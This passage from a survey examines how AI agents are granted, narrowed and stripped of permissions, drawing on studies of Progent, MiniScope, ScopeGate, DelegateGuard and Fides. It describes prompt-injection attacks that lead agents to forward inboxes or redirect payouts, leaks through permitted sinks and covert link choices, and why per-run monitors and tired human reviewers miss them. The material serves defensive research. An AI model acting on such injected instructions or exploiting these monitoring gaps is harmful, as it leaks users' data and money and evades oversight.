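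The service also has to find one approval that satisfies every condition. Suppose a support ticket has moved from version 7 to version 8. The approval for version 7 is still active, but someone has withdrawn the approval for version 8. A service that looks separately for an active approval and for an approval of the current version will find both, although no active approval covers the change. *Are You Still the Agent I Authorized?* (2026) likewise requires a single valid lease (a temporary grant) to cover each action in full.

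When one service holds the approval and another performs the action, a single operation cannot easily cover both. In Santos-Grueiro's design, the approval service issues a one-use reservation for the exact action, and the other service uses it up as it performs the action. The reservation stays valid until it expires, even if someone withdraws the original approval. A short expiry time narrows this gap, but valid actions can fail if they take too long. When sixteen workers shared one client process on a desktop computer, almost none of their writes finished within 100 milliseconds, even though each worker had its own target. Given ten seconds, all of them finished. On cloud machines, with a separate process for each worker, more than 95% finished within 100 milliseconds.

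### Work and grants that the agent has passed on

Stopping an agent does not necessarily stop the work it has started elsewhere. *Authorization Revocation for Long-Running AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) describes a controller that cancels a task, revokes its token and sees its process exit. A message the agent queued earlier can still cause a remote worker to complete a reservation. The Model Context Protocol and A2A, a protocol for communication between agents, treat cancellation as a request and do not guarantee that the work has stopped. Zhu and Wang therefore place a barrier at the service where the action would take effect. In their tests, the service accepted a late action in three runs without the barrier and refused the same kind of action in two runs with it.

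Revoking everything downstream of an agent can also be wrong. In *ResidualAuth*, Choi, Jeong and colleagues (2026) consider an organisation that gives one agent access to data, which that agent passes to a second. If the organisation later revokes the first agent's grant, the second should lose access too, unless the organisation has also granted it access directly. Before the revocation, each agent has the same permissions with or without that direct grant, so a list of current permissions doesn't show whether the second agent should keep its access.

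Choi and colleagues calculated how much a system has to remember to get every such decision right. Without revocation, it needs about N bits for N agents and one permission, to record whether each agent has it. With revocation and unrestricted delegation, it may have to record every direct grant. The organisation can make N grants and the agents can make N(N − 1) among themselves, which gives

N + N(N − 1) = N² bits

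For ten agents, that is 100 bits instead of 10, which a database can easily store. Language models are a poor place to keep this record. Choi and colleagues gave four models 16 pairs of cases in which the same revocation called for opposite decisions. With a short extract of the past events, the models got both cases right in 0 to 2 pairs. When they also received the correct decision from a trusted ledger, they got both right in 15 or 16 pairs. The low scores partly reflect missing information, because the extract could omit the grant that mattered. A ledger outside the model would preserve that information.

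### Ending a grant too early

Suppose the tests pass and PORTICO closes the grant, but the agent then notices that it left out a case in the serialization file. If the contract provides no way to reopen access, the agent cannot finish. In a supplementary set of 42 pairings of real-project tasks with models, PORTICO completed 31, while a system that kept grants open completed all 42. Santos-Grueiro attributes the gap to contracts that closed grants too early or lacked a way to renew them, and to models that did not ask for a new grant.

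The loss was smaller on the controlled coding tasks, where PORTICO completed 161 of 185 runs, compared with 180 for a fixed list of allowed tools and paths. PORTICO stayed within the contract in every run, compared with 92% of runs for the fixed list. A version of PORTICO that kept the initial permissions but allowed no requests completed only 21% of runs, so most runs could not be completed without temporary grants.

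An operator can add a trusted event that reopens access, such as a new phase of work or a person's approval. According to *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, however, frequent approval requests tire people and encourage broad "remember my approval" grants. Such grants would bring back lingering authority. The operator could also close the grant at the end of the editing phase instead of at the first passing test. The agent could then correct the missed case without asking, but the file would be exposed to injected instructions for longer.

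## Who chooses what the code may do?

PORTICO can open and close a grant at the right moments only because an operator has already listed the files the grant may cover. Other enforcement mechanisms depend on such a choice too. In *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026) explicitly assume that the policy their system enforces already exists, and they leave its content to others.

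Enforcement can ensure that the code receives no permissions its caller lacks and uses only those it was granted. It cannot bring the grant closer to what the job needs, because a file mount or a signed token contains no information about the job's purpose. Ordinary use does not reliably correct the grant either, because a missing permission causes an error while an extra one goes unnoticed.

An operator can choose G by writing fixed rules, a model can choose it by reading the user's request, or the user can choose it by answering prompts or picking a file.

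### Rules written in advance

A fixed policy suits narrow, repetitive work because nothing an agent reads can change it, but it suits a general assistant badly. In *The Structure of Authority*, Miller, Tulloh and Shapiro (2005) objected to static policy files because the authority a program needs changes as it runs, and nobody knows it beforehand. They thought adding authority bit by bit through security dialogs was no better, because the dialogs would make the program unbearable to use.

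Adam and colleagues give an example with two innocent requests. A user asks an agent to set up a new project by copying a configuration file from another project, and later asks it to publish the new project on GitHub. The configuration file contains a private key, so the key becomes public. The researchers saw Claude 4.5 Haiku do this. A fixed policy could have prevented it only with a blanket restriction, such as blocking network access, and the researchers expect users to switch off such a restriction quickly. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes sandboxes as safe but a lot of work to maintain, because someone has to configure each new capability.

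Fixed grants also tend to be too broad. *MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) examined the connectors that link ChatGPT and Claude to services such as Gmail, and found that six requested broader permissions than their tools required. ChatGPT's Gmail connector was advertised as only reading mail, but its permissions covered 50 operations when 32 would have been enough, and they allowed it to change and delete mail. The connectors' developers knew exactly which tools they offered, so they were better placed than most operators to choose a narrow grant.

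### Offering a tool and authorising a call

A list of tools determines whether an agent can issue refunds, but not whether it may refund a particular amount to a particular account. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) checked whether popular agent software determines the second. The June 2026 audit covered the public source code of LangChain/LangGraph and LlamaIndex, which developers use to build agents, and of the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to the payment company Stripe.

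By default, none of them blocked calls whose argument values violated a policy. LangChain and LlamaIndex look up the tool the model names and run it with the model's arguments. A type check may reject a malformed account number, but it accepts an attacker's account number if the format is right. Stripe's toolkit can limit the kinds of action available, and the developer can give it a key with restricted permissions. Within those limits, it forwards whatever amount and customer the model supplies.

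Developers can add their own checks or require human approval, so the audit is a criticism of the defaults, not a report of a specific vulnerability. It did not cover Stripe's remote server, which might perform more checks.

In a demonstration with a simulated payment service, Mellafe Zuvic had LangChain process a call that changed a merchant's payout account to the attacker's. LangChain ran it. The same call failed when it first had to pass through ScopeGate, Mellafe Zuvic's own checker, which works like this:

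1. The operator's policy must list the tool.
2. Each restricted argument must have a value on the operator's approved list.
3. A payment must be an ordinary, finite number between zero and a set maximum.
4. Where the policy requires it, the call must come with a trusted key that identifies the request, to limit repeated payments.
5. ScopeGate refuses everything else, including any call that causes an error during the check.

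ScopeGate allowed none of 48 fixed attack inputs, which included look-alike letters, invisible characters and misspelled tool names. These tests had exposed a flaw in an earlier version, which checked only whether the amount exceeded the maximum. NaN, a special value that programming languages use for results that are not numbers, passed this check because a greater-than comparison with NaN is always false.

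Mellafe Zuvic then let another model, GLM-5.2, attack ScopeGate for 40 rounds and told it why each attempt had failed. GLM-5.2 made 29 unauthorised attempts, and ScopeGate refused them all. The other rounds produced 9 malformed calls and 2 harmless calls that ScopeGate allowed. In a separate test, ScopeGate allowed all 10 legitimate calls.

These are small tests by a single author, who also built ScopeGate. They show that ScopeGate applied its approved list correctly, but not that an operator would write the right list. If the operator had put the attacker's account on the list by mistake, ScopeGate would have approved the payout.

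### Binding a tool to one customer

Suppose a company has 10,000 customers, and its support assistant may have to refund any of them. If the operator writes one approved list for all conversations, it has to contain all 10,000. Text injected into one conversation could then request a refund for a different customer, and the value would pass the check. The harness can instead follow Ubl and Arora's advice and make a new tool for each conversation:

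```
function refund_tool(customer):
    return function refund(amount):
        payments.refund(customer, amount)
```

The harness takes the customer's number from the login and gives the model only `refund(amount)`. This bound tool can refund only the customer who logged in, whereas the general tool can refund any customer. Both allow the same amounts, so with 10,000 customers, the bound tool permits one ten-thousandth of the calls that the general tool does.

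The model cannot choose another customer because the tool has no argument for one. It also cannot use look-alike characters to get around this restriction, because the harness never interprets a customer number from the model. An approved list with a single entry would permit the same refunds, but the harness would have to write a new list for each conversation. Neither method limits the refund amount, which needs a separate maximum.

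Binding works only if the harness has the right value before the model starts. A login identifies the customer, but if a user asks an agent to pay the bill in yesterday's email, the recipient's account number is in the email.

### Progent lets a model draft the policy

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, address this problem with a policy that changes during the task. A language model drafts the rules, and ordinary code decides which changes can take effect without approval. In their example, the user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice:

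1. The policy model sees the user's request and the list of tools. It writes a policy that allows only a search for Alice's email.
2. The email asks for a summary of recent mail, posted to the user's account on the messaging service Slack. The policy model proposes adding tools to read mail, look up the user's Slack name and send Slack messages. This widens the policy, so it needs approval.
3. The lookup returns the name `alice`. The policy model proposes allowing Slack messages only to `alice`. This narrows the policy, so it takes effect automatically.
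4. A recent email contains an injected instruction to forward the whole inbox to an attacker. If this fools the policy model into proposing a rule that allows it, Progent detects the widening and asks for approval.

Progent blocks any call that no rule allows, so the inbox stays private unless someone approves the change in step 4.

The rules consist of simple conditions on tool names and arguments, such as comparisons, lists and text patterns. This lets Progent compare two policies with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all be true together. If A(P) is the set of calls that policy P allows, a new policy P′ takes effect automatically only if

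A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

The solver searches for a call that P′ allows and P does not. If no such call exists, the change is a narrowing. Replacing one permitted recipient with another counts as a widening, even though the number of recipients stays the same.

The operator decides who may approve a change that widens permissions. Progent can refer each such change to a person, approve those for particular tools, refuse them all or approve them all.

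Shi and colleagues used GPT-4o both as the agent and as the policy model. On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On ASB, another benchmark of injected instructions, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agent completed about as many tasks with Progent as without it. But in these tests Progent automatically approved every change that widened the policy, to simulate a careless user. The results therefore measure how well the model drafted policies and don't show how much the solver's check added.

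On AgentDojo, 2.5% of attacks succeeded when the model wrote a policy from the user's request and never changed it. No attacks succeeded when a person reviewed the first policy and every change that widened it, though the researchers assumed a reviewer with strong security awareness. Only 6% of changes widened the policy, so a reviewer would see few requests.

Most failures on ASB involved attack tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of tools the task needed. Shi and colleagues stopped these attacks with handwritten rules, which required someone to know which tools to trust.

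### MiniScope calculates the smallest grant

MiniScope, the system Zhu and colleagues built, uses a calculation instead of a model to choose permissions. It works with services that use OAuth scopes, named permissions that each cover a set of operations. The agent submits a plan that lists the operations it wants to perform. MiniScope then chooses the scopes that

minimise Σ cost(s) · x(s)

where x(s) is 1 if it selects scope s and 0 if it does not, and the selected scopes must cover every operation in the plan. The cost of a scope is the number of operations it permits. The calculation is necessary because scopes overlap. In Google Calendar, more than one scope permits 24 of the 37 operations.

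If the agent does not yet have the selected scopes, MiniScope prompts the user to grant them once, for the session, or permanently. Only the user can widen the grant. MiniScope keeps the user's real credentials and adds them to each permitted request.

Zhu and colleagues also asked language models to choose the scopes. Three commercial models, including GPT-5, matched MiniScope's choice in 70–83% of cases, and two open-weight models did so in 20–34%. The models did worst on requests that involved several services. On these requests, the scopes Qwen3-30B chose permitted 2.19 times as many operations as MiniScope's, and GPT-5's permitted 1.12 times as many. MiniScope added 1–6% to the time a request took. A language model generated all the requests, so they may not match what people ask for.

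Which grant is smallest depends on how one measures size. Suppose an operation is available through two scopes, one that also permits deleting events and one that also permits reading the guest list. Each covers two operations and neither contains the other, so counting operations cannot determine which is safer. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) points out that MiniScope settles such cases with penalty weights and does not discuss whether the best answer is unique. An operator can change the weights, for example to penalize deletion heavily.

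A more serious limitation is that MiniScope finds the least authority that the agent's plan needs, and an attacker may have changed the plan. In one of the paper's examples, a user asks the agent to reply to an email that contains an instruction to delete it afterwards, and the agent adds the deletion to its plan. MiniScope correctly calculates that this requires full access to Gmail and prompts the user to grant it. The protection then depends on the user noticing that a reply should not require deletion.

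MiniScope also does not check argument values. A scope for sending Slack messages usually lets the agent write to anyone in the workspace. Zhu and colleagues suggest a possible extension that would limit messages to the recipient named in the plan, but they warn that more detailed permission requests could overwhelm users.

### How well do users review requests?

Users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Most prompts concern harmless commands, so this rate alone does not show that people are careless. Anthropic therefore ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, replacing the text of one prompt during a coding session with a clearly dangerous command. Of these testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

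The testers were not working on their own projects and knew they were being evaluated, so they may have worried less about damage. Anthropic also had a reason to publicise the result, because it was replacing most prompts with auto mode, in which a classifier model reviews each action. The classifier blocked 89% of the same commands, more than the testers did, but a fixed limit that excluded those commands would have blocked them all.

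Permission prompts also lead people to create broad permanent rules. Anthropic found that almost half of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule approving some shell commands in advance. Many of these rules let the agent run any Python or Node program, which is practically the same as letting it run any command. The share of users with such rules was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks. Auto mode ignores the broadest rules.

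*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of agents damaging files and found that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, the user had switched on automatic approval. In 31, the prompt did not show what the command would do. For example, a prompt to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine but does not show what the code in that file does. In *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), software practitioners described clicking through familiar prompts because they were tired or rushed. Past approvals are therefore a poor guide to what a user wants to permit.

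People might do better if they set rules calmly in advance. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested this with 113 people who did not work in software. They supervised a simulated assistant through 18 actions, 7 of which exceeded the user's request, such as buying a lounge pass or reading private messages. One group decided whether to approve each action. In the second group, a model allowed some actions and referred the rest to the participant. The third group set rules in advance for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each.

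| Who decided | Prompts per person | Unrequested actions blocked | Unrequested actions approved when prompted |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user, for every action | 18.0 | 59.6% | 40.3% |
| A model, with doubtful cases referred to the user | 10.0 | 53.9% | 46.1% |
| The user's own rules | 10.9 | 39.6% | 66.8% |

The people who wrote rules blocked the fewest unrequested actions. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed most decisions, and then approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions that came up. The study was small, and Yan did not randomly assign some of the later participants in the rule-writing group. Even so, the result is a reason not to assume that users will write narrow rules.

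Yan's participants refused far more actions than Anthropic's testers did. Yan's prompts described each action in plain language, including the recipient or amount, and each session had at most 18 prompts. Both differences may have helped people refuse more, although the studies also differed in participants and tasks.

### Choosing a file as a way of granting it

A user can also grant access without answering a security question. Miller, Tulloh and Shapiro return to the two Unix commands for copying a file, `cp` and `cat`. `cp` receives file names, while `cat` receives files that the shell has already opened. No operator can write a narrow policy for `cp` in advance, because the user might name any file. With `cat`, the user has to name the two files anyway, and naming them in the command gives the program exactly the access it needs.

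They describe two systems that extend this idea to windows and menus. CapDesk is a desktop for programs written in the language E, and Polaris is an HP Labs prototype for existing Windows programs. Under Polaris, opening a spreadsheet in Excel works like this:

1. Polaris runs Excel in a separate account that starts with almost no access.
2. The user picks `killer.xls` by double-clicking it or selecting it in a file chooser.
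3. Polaris gives Excel access to that file.

A hostile macro in the spreadsheet can damage that file but cannot search the user's other documents. Polaris needs no extra prompt, because the user would have picked the file on an ordinary computer too. According to Miller and colleagues, people who used Polaris regularly left macros switched on.

The desktop software needs all the user's authority to pass on parts of it, so a flaw there would expose everything. Some authority also does not correspond to anything the user would naturally select while working. For example, a mail program needs continuing access to a mail server, which the user grants in its settings. Picking a file also does not always indicate what the program may do with it. Excel receives permission to edit the spreadsheet even if the user only wants to read it.

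An assistant could use the same method for the sales chart. If the user drags `sales.csv` into the conversation, the harness can open that file and give the script read-only access. If the user types "chart last year's sales", the model has to find the file, and the script's access depends on the name the model chooses. The harness could then show a file chooser with the model's suggestion highlighted. The user would again have to answer a prompt, but it would be more informative than a request to approve a command. Confirming files this way would quickly become tedious for a task that involves hundreds of them.

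### May a model that has read untrusted text set its own limits?

Mellafe Zuvic argues that letting a model set the limits on its own calls is circular, because an injection that makes the model attempt a forbidden call could also make it change the limits to allow that call. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) raises a similar concern about Progent, whose policy model reads tool results that may contain hostile instructions.

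The argument is convincing when the model widens permissions, but not when it narrows them. If the harness applies L ∩ M to the model's proposal M, as in Bastion's design, the model can only remove permissions. Hostile text can then make the job fail, but it cannot add c. It could also defeat the purpose of a narrowing. In Progent's example, an attacker who controlled the Slack lookup could get the policy model to restrict messages to the wrong person, but the earlier policy already allowed messages to that person. A complete ban on model-written limits would therefore give up useful narrowing, and the harness could already block any widening that the ban would prevent.

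Progent's experiments also suggest that a model exposed to hostile text often still sets reasonable limits. When every widening of the policy was approved automatically, 1.0% of attacks succeeded, compared with 2.5% under a policy that never changed. Three kinds of attack that Shi and colleagues aimed at the policy model raised the success rate only slightly. But a low average on a benchmark doesn't guarantee safety, because an attacker needs only one widening that works.

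A model that has read only the user's request avoids the circularity. Such a model writes Progent's first policy. One also sets the ceiling in CapScope, and Bouras and colleagues freeze that ceiling before any agent reads a file's contents. Mellafe Zuvic's rule bars all model output from the policy, even rules that a model drafted long before the task, because someone may have tampered with the model itself. An operator can follow this stricter rule for a list of payout accounts, but cannot write a policy by hand for every request to a general assistant.

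The user's request may not be trustworthy either. Zhu and colleagues note that people paste text from web pages into their prompts, and that this text can contain an injection. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* warns that a manipulated prompt may lead a system to grant more authority than the user intended. A harness can reduce this risk by keeping pasted text and attachments away from the model that drafts the policy.

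Someone still has to decide whether to widen a policy. Fewer prompts should help, but Anthropic's testers missed most dangerous commands even early in a session. Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans it presents for approval, compared with 3% of permission prompts. They may reject plans because they dislike the proposed work rather than because they spot a danger, but they evidently read them. The start of a task is therefore a promising time to ask about its limits. For sensitive work, an operator can have Progent refuse every widening, but tasks such as Alice's will then stop as soon as they need a tool that the first policy left out.

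## What can go wrong inside a correctly narrowed grant?

Suppose an operator gives a code-review agent exactly the permissions its job requires. The agent may read a confidential report about an unpublished security flaw and post comments on the project's public page. It can still paste the report into a comment. Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues (2026), in *DelegateGuard*, built a system that narrows authority at every handover and examined which attacks it could not stop.

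### DelegateGuard's grants

A trusted program called the adapter turns the user's request into a first grant, which has seven fields:

G = ⟨h, p, L, O, S, d, r⟩

In one example, an orchestrator summarises a confidential contract and asks a second agent to format the summary.

| Field | Meaning | The formatting agent's grant |
|---|---|---|
| h | Holder | The formatting agent |
| p | Purpose | `contract.summarize/format` |
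| L | Labels of the data it may handle | Confidential contract clauses |
| O | Operations | Transform, transmit |
| S | Sinks | The reply to the user |
| d | Remaining delegation depth | Lower than the orchestrator's |
| r | Whether someone has revoked the grant | No |

The orchestrator can create this grant only if it meets all of these conditions:

- The child's purpose is the same as the parent's or falls under it, as `contract.summarize/format` falls under `contract.summarize`.
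- L(child) ⊆ L(parent), O(child) ⊆ O(parent) and S(child) ⊆ S(parent).
- d(child) < d(parent), so a grant with a depth of 0 allows no further delegation.

If the orchestrator tries to add an outside web address that its own grant lacks, DelegateGuard stops the grant from reaching the formatting agent.

A reference monitor then checks every action that moves data. The agent must hold the grant, and the grant must cover the action's purpose, operation, labels and sink. Every grant in the chain back to the user must also still be active. Revoking one grant therefore disables every grant below it, which matters if a sub-agent is still waiting in a queue when the user cancels the task. Each check takes one or two microseconds.

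### A permitted sink that outsiders can read

None of these checks looks at what a message contains. Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that this leaves a gap, which they state as Proposition 1. Suppose a monitor decides based on the holder, purpose, labels, operation, sink and chain of grants, but ignores the content and volume of the data. If it permits a sink that outsiders can observe, then some run exists in which it lets an arbitrary secret out through that sink. The proof is short:

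1. Take a harmless message that the monitor permits through the sink.
2. Replace its text with the secret, and keep everything the monitor checks the same.
3. The monitor ignores the text and its length, so it permits this message too.
4. An outsider reads the secret at the sink.

The same reasoning applies to a macaroon, a file mount or CapScope's permission store. Step 2 assumes that the secret can be sent under labels the grant permits. It can in the code-review case because the agent has to write about the confidential flaw to do its job. An agent might also declare the wrong labels. DelegateGuard is designed for the software that fetches data to label it, but in these tests the agent declared the labels on what it sent.

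To see how much this gap matters, the researchers wrote 26 attacks on five office workflows. Some tried to use a forbidden sink or widen a grant. Others stayed within the grant but, for example, left out a label or passed data through shared memory. An attack counted as a leak if secret data reached a place the attacker could observe.

| Defence | Leaks from 26 attacks | Legitimate actions blocked, out of 5 |
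|---|---|---|
| None | 18 | 0 |
| Fixed list of allowed sinks | 3 | 0 |
| Labels checked against sinks | 3 | 0 |
| Search of outgoing text for the secret | 0 | 4 |
| DelegateGuard | 3 | 0 |

All three of DelegateGuard's leaks went through the public code-review comments. The text search stopped every leak, but it also blocked confidential text that the task required sending to the user or to an internal note.

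On this measure, DelegateGuard did no better than a fixed list, but it did better in two further tests of five cases each. In the first, a sub-agent tried to send data after the user had cancelled the task. In the second, it tried to send the wrong kind of data to a permitted sink. DelegateGuard blocked all ten attempts, and the fixed list allowed them all.

A larger study ran the five workflows 90 times, half of them with an injection, and let the agents exchange messages and try again after a refusal. Without restrictions, 38 of the 45 attacked runs leaked. With DelegateGuard, 9 leaked, and all 45 runs without an attack completed their tasks. The remaining leaks were all in the code review workflow, where every attacked run leaked.

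The agent in this study was Qwen2.5-7B, a small model that is easy to mislead. In a simpler test, it proposed the attacker's action in 42 of 45 cases, and the smaller Llama-3.2-3B did so in 44. A current model would probably leak less without any protection, so DelegateGuard would reduce its leaks by less than the drop from 0.844 suggests. Leaks through code review still occurred in a supporting test that included two models of about 70 billion parameters.

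The adapter's choices mattered as much as the monitor. When the researchers added one outside web address to the first grant for convenience, 30 of 45 attacks succeeded, although the monitor worked as before. It stopped the other 15, which relied on revoked grants. Most other mistakes in the grant made no difference or blocked legitimate work.

### Harmless steps that add up

A monitor can also approve every step of a harmful sequence. *The Causal Impact of Tool Affordance on Safety Alignment in LLM Agents* (2026) gives the example of a payment service with a limit of $1,000 per transaction. When asked to move $2,000, a chatbot without tools refused because of the limit, but an agent with a payment tool made two transfers of $1,000. Nothing capped the total, as with a budget that applies to each token separately.

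*Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) tested a similar failure with a calendar assistant. The user had agreed to a limit on total disclosure. Each message the assistant sent was acceptable on its own, but together the messages could exceed that limit. Qwen3-30B exceeded it in 22 of 60 runs. A guard that compared each action with the task's purpose reduced the failures only to 20. A guard that kept a running total prevented all of them and blocked none of the 120 harmless control runs. A second model, Gemma-4, never exceeded the limit, even without a guard.

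A running total works when an operator knows what to add up, such as money or calendar entries. Other combinations are harder to anticipate. *AGATE* (2026) describes attacks that spread a harmful effect over ordinary steps such as reading a file, editing a configuration and installing a package. With 20 tools, there are 20⁵, or 3.2 million, possible sequences of five calls, ignoring their arguments. An operator can't review them all, and blocking every tool that could form part of a harmful sequence would leave the agent able to do very little.

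### Commands that reveal protected files

A permitted command can have effects that its name does not suggest. With CapScope's test runner, for example, permission to run tests is also permission to run any code in the test files. *The Compiler May Read It, the Agent May Not* (Roy, 2026) describes another case, in which a permitted program reads files that the agent is not allowed to read.

Roy uses Claude Code to work on a program that simulates fluid flow. Some source files contain unpublished or licensed scientific models. The agent must not read these files, because everything it reads goes into a transcript that leaves the machine, but the compiler needs them to build the simulation. The agent starts the compiler from its own shell and under the same account, so neither the permission rules nor the sandbox can distinguish the compiler's reads from the agent's.

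Roy listed fifteen ways in which the text of a protected file could reach the agent, and worked out which of them the existing settings would block:

| What blocks the route | Number of routes |
|---|---|
| Permission rules and sandbox | 2 |
| Sandbox only | 7 |
| Permission rules only | 1 |
| Neither | 5 |

The five open routes are a compiler mode that prints source code, the instructions inside a permitted build, the project's version history, a tool server, and a hook. Most of the route classifications come from documentation and reasoning. Roy had seen two of the fifteen routes refused in practice and did not test the other thirteen, partly because a successful test on the real files would have disclosed their contents.

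Blocking more commands did not solve the problem. Over five weeks, Roy's list of forbidden patterns grew from 14 rules to 586. The last revision added 30 rules for 15 commands that had already been blocked for a protected folder but not for a protected file. The compiler route stayed open throughout because the build depends on it.

An ordinary user could instead keep the protected files under a separate account. A broker running under that account would build the project on request and send the agent a filtered reply. Security then depends on what the filter lets through. The agent can't see what to fix if the reply is only "passed" or "failed", but some of the compiler's error messages will quote protected lines. The finished program also contains numerical constants from the protected models. Roy accepts the error messages, and protected content can still leak through the compiler.

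The same problem arises when a credential proxy returns a service's full response, because the agent can read any private data that the hidden token gives access to.

### Leaks through behaviour

Even a filter that removes every protected word cannot stop a program from revealing data through its behaviour. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, asked how a customer could run someone else's program on private data without the program revealing the data to anyone else. The obvious leaks are saved files and messages to other programs. Less obviously, the program could encode data in the amount it charges, because its owner receives a copy of the bill. It could also vary how heavily it uses the processor or disk, which another program on the same machine could detect as a change in speed.

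Lampson called this last kind of route a covert channel, meaning one that nobody intended for passing information. A confined program could not leak data through such channels if the customer determined in advance everything the program put into them, including its effect on the machine's speed. The operating system would then have to enforce this, for example by slowing the program down or adding meaningless disk activity. Since these measures make the system less efficient, Lampson suggested that some customers might accept a limit on how fast data could leak. Steven Lipner replied in 1975 that closing covert channels seemed to carry an "unreasonable performance penalty", according to lecture slides from Purdue University.

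An observer who can distinguish k outcomes learns at most log₂ k bits from each one. A choice among four web links therefore reveals up to 2 bits, and six such choices reveal up to 12 bits, enough to identify one of 4,096 possibilities.

*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) showed that the web links an agent follows can reveal what it is working on. The attacker controls a website and places a link to it on a page the agent visits. The site offers references on several subjects, and the agent follows the one that fits its task. Further choices narrow the subject down. The agent sends no private text, and each request is an ordinary part of web research.

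Across four agents and three models, the attack recovered the concepts in users' questions with an average F1 score of 0.89. F1 runs from 0 to 1 and is higher when more of the right concepts are found and fewer wrong ones are added. The attack needed about six choices per question. It also built profiles of users over several conversations, with a score of 0.80.

The researchers' defence breaks the link between what the agent needs and what it requests. The agent downloads a fixed number of pages, chosen without reference to the private task, and selects among the copies on its own machine. This lowered both scores to 0.39, so some information still leaked. *AgenticOS* (2026) proposes similar measures for other channels, such as sending requests in fixed time windows and padding outputs to a standard size. It aims to make leaks too slow to be of much use, and accepts that they cannot be eliminated.

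Monitors have trouble with such leaks because each action looks harmless on its own. Pandey et al. give the example of an assistant that may tell colleagues when its user is free, but not why the user is busy. In one run, a busy slot is an ordinary meeting, and the assistant offers slot 10. In another, the same busy slot is a confidential job interview, and the assistant offers slot 11. Both offers are truthful, but if the assistant's choice depends on why the user is busy, a colleague can learn something about the reason.

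Under the rule the assistant breaks, two runs with the same free and busy times should produce the same offer. A single run can't break this rule, so a monitor that looks at one run at a time and never raises a false alarm must approve every run and miss every violation. The theorem follows almost directly from how the rule defines a violation, but the difficulty it describes is real because most monitors check only one run.

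Nine language models acting as judges had the same difficulty. Eight approved the assistant's behaviour in all 30 trials when they reviewed each action separately, but eight detected the problem every time when they saw both runs together. In a separate test, Claude Sonnet 4.6 did the scheduling with no such leak in 80 trials, so a good model may avoid the problem even if a monitor can't detect it.

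A narrower grant would help here. If the part of the assistant that writes the offer receives only the free and busy times, its choice cannot depend on the reason for a meeting. This adds a step, and the assistant can no longer use those reasons to make better suggestions.

### Results that return to the caller

The downstream rule limits what a caller passes to a program, but not what the program sends back. Suppose the sales script runs in a perfect sandbox with access to one CSV file and one chart. It prints a few rows so the assistant can check the totals, and one row contains an injected instruction in its comment column. The assistant reads that row while it still has access to the database and mail.

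Suppose the script holds a set of privileges G and the assistant holds a set A, with G ⊆ A. While the script runs, hostile text in the file can cause the misuse of only the privileges in G. But if the script's output includes that text, it could lead the assistant to misuse any privilege in A. This can happen even when the script has no bugs and stays within its grant.

Bouras and colleagues treat file contents and command output as untrusted in CapScope. Such text can still cause the orchestrator to request any privilege under the task's ceiling, which may explain the three attacks that still succeed against CapScope.

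A returned result can also be misleading without containing any instruction. *Trust the Brand, Lose Control* (2026) describes an orchestrator that asked another agent to free disk space with an installed cleaning tool. The tool's script contained hidden destructive commands. The second agent ran the script and reported recovering 476 MB. The orchestrator accepted the report without asking anyone to check what else had changed.

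One defence is to have another model inspect the result first. *WebMCP-Phalanx* (2026) sends suspicious tool output to an agent that has no tools and cleans the output before the main agent sees it. The inspecting agent has no authority to misuse, but it may fail to recognise a well-disguised instruction.

*L3M* (2026) instead restricts the form of the answer. For example, a main agent sorts bug reports without reading them. A separate program gives each report to a fresh sub-agent, which has no network or project access, and asks whether the report describes a fault in one component. The program passes only one of three fixed answers to the main agent. Each report can therefore convey at most log₂ 3, or about 1.6, bits to the main agent, as long as timing and failures reveal nothing more. The protection is lost if the main agent also opens the report.

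A short answer leaves no room for an instruction, but it can still be false. An attacker can write a report that produces the wrong one of the three answers, and the agent may then close a real bug or spend hours on an invented one. The number of bits in the answer limits how many outcomes the attacker can choose from, but not how harmful each one is. An operator therefore has to make sure that every answer on the list leads to an acceptable action.

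For the sales chart, the harness could accept only the image file and a number for the total. The assistant could then show the chart to the user without reading any text from the CSV file. The assistant should not look at the image, because an image can also contain written instructions.

### What Fides adds

Information-flow control addresses several of these problems. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies it in Fides, a planner developed at Microsoft. A planner is the part of an AI agent that decides when to query the model and when to call a tool.

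Each piece of data has two labels. One states whether it comes from a trusted source, and the other lists who may read it. When a model combines several pieces, the result gets the most restrictive combination of their labels. If one input is untrusted, the result is untrusted. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read document x, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read document y, then the readers of a summary of both are

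{Alice, Bob, Carol} ∩ {Bob, Carol, Dan} = {Bob, Carol}

Fides checks these labels against two main policies. An action with serious consequences, such as a payment, may go ahead only if untrusted data did not influence it. A message may go out only if every recipient is allowed to read its contents. An operator can require both policies for a tool, or accept either one.

These policies would quickly stop most work if the planning model read every email, because everything it did afterwards would count as untrusted. Fides therefore stores untrusted text in variables and shows the model only their names. If the user asks the agent to check recent emails for a meeting request and add it to the calendar, Fides can proceed like this:

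1. The agent fetches three emails, and Fides stores their text in a variable.
2. The planning model asks a second model, which has no tools, whether the emails contain a meeting request. The second model can answer only yes or no.
3. The planning model reads the answer.
4. If the answer is yes, the second model extracts the date, time and participants into another variable.
5. The planning model passes that variable to the calendar tool without seeing what it contains.

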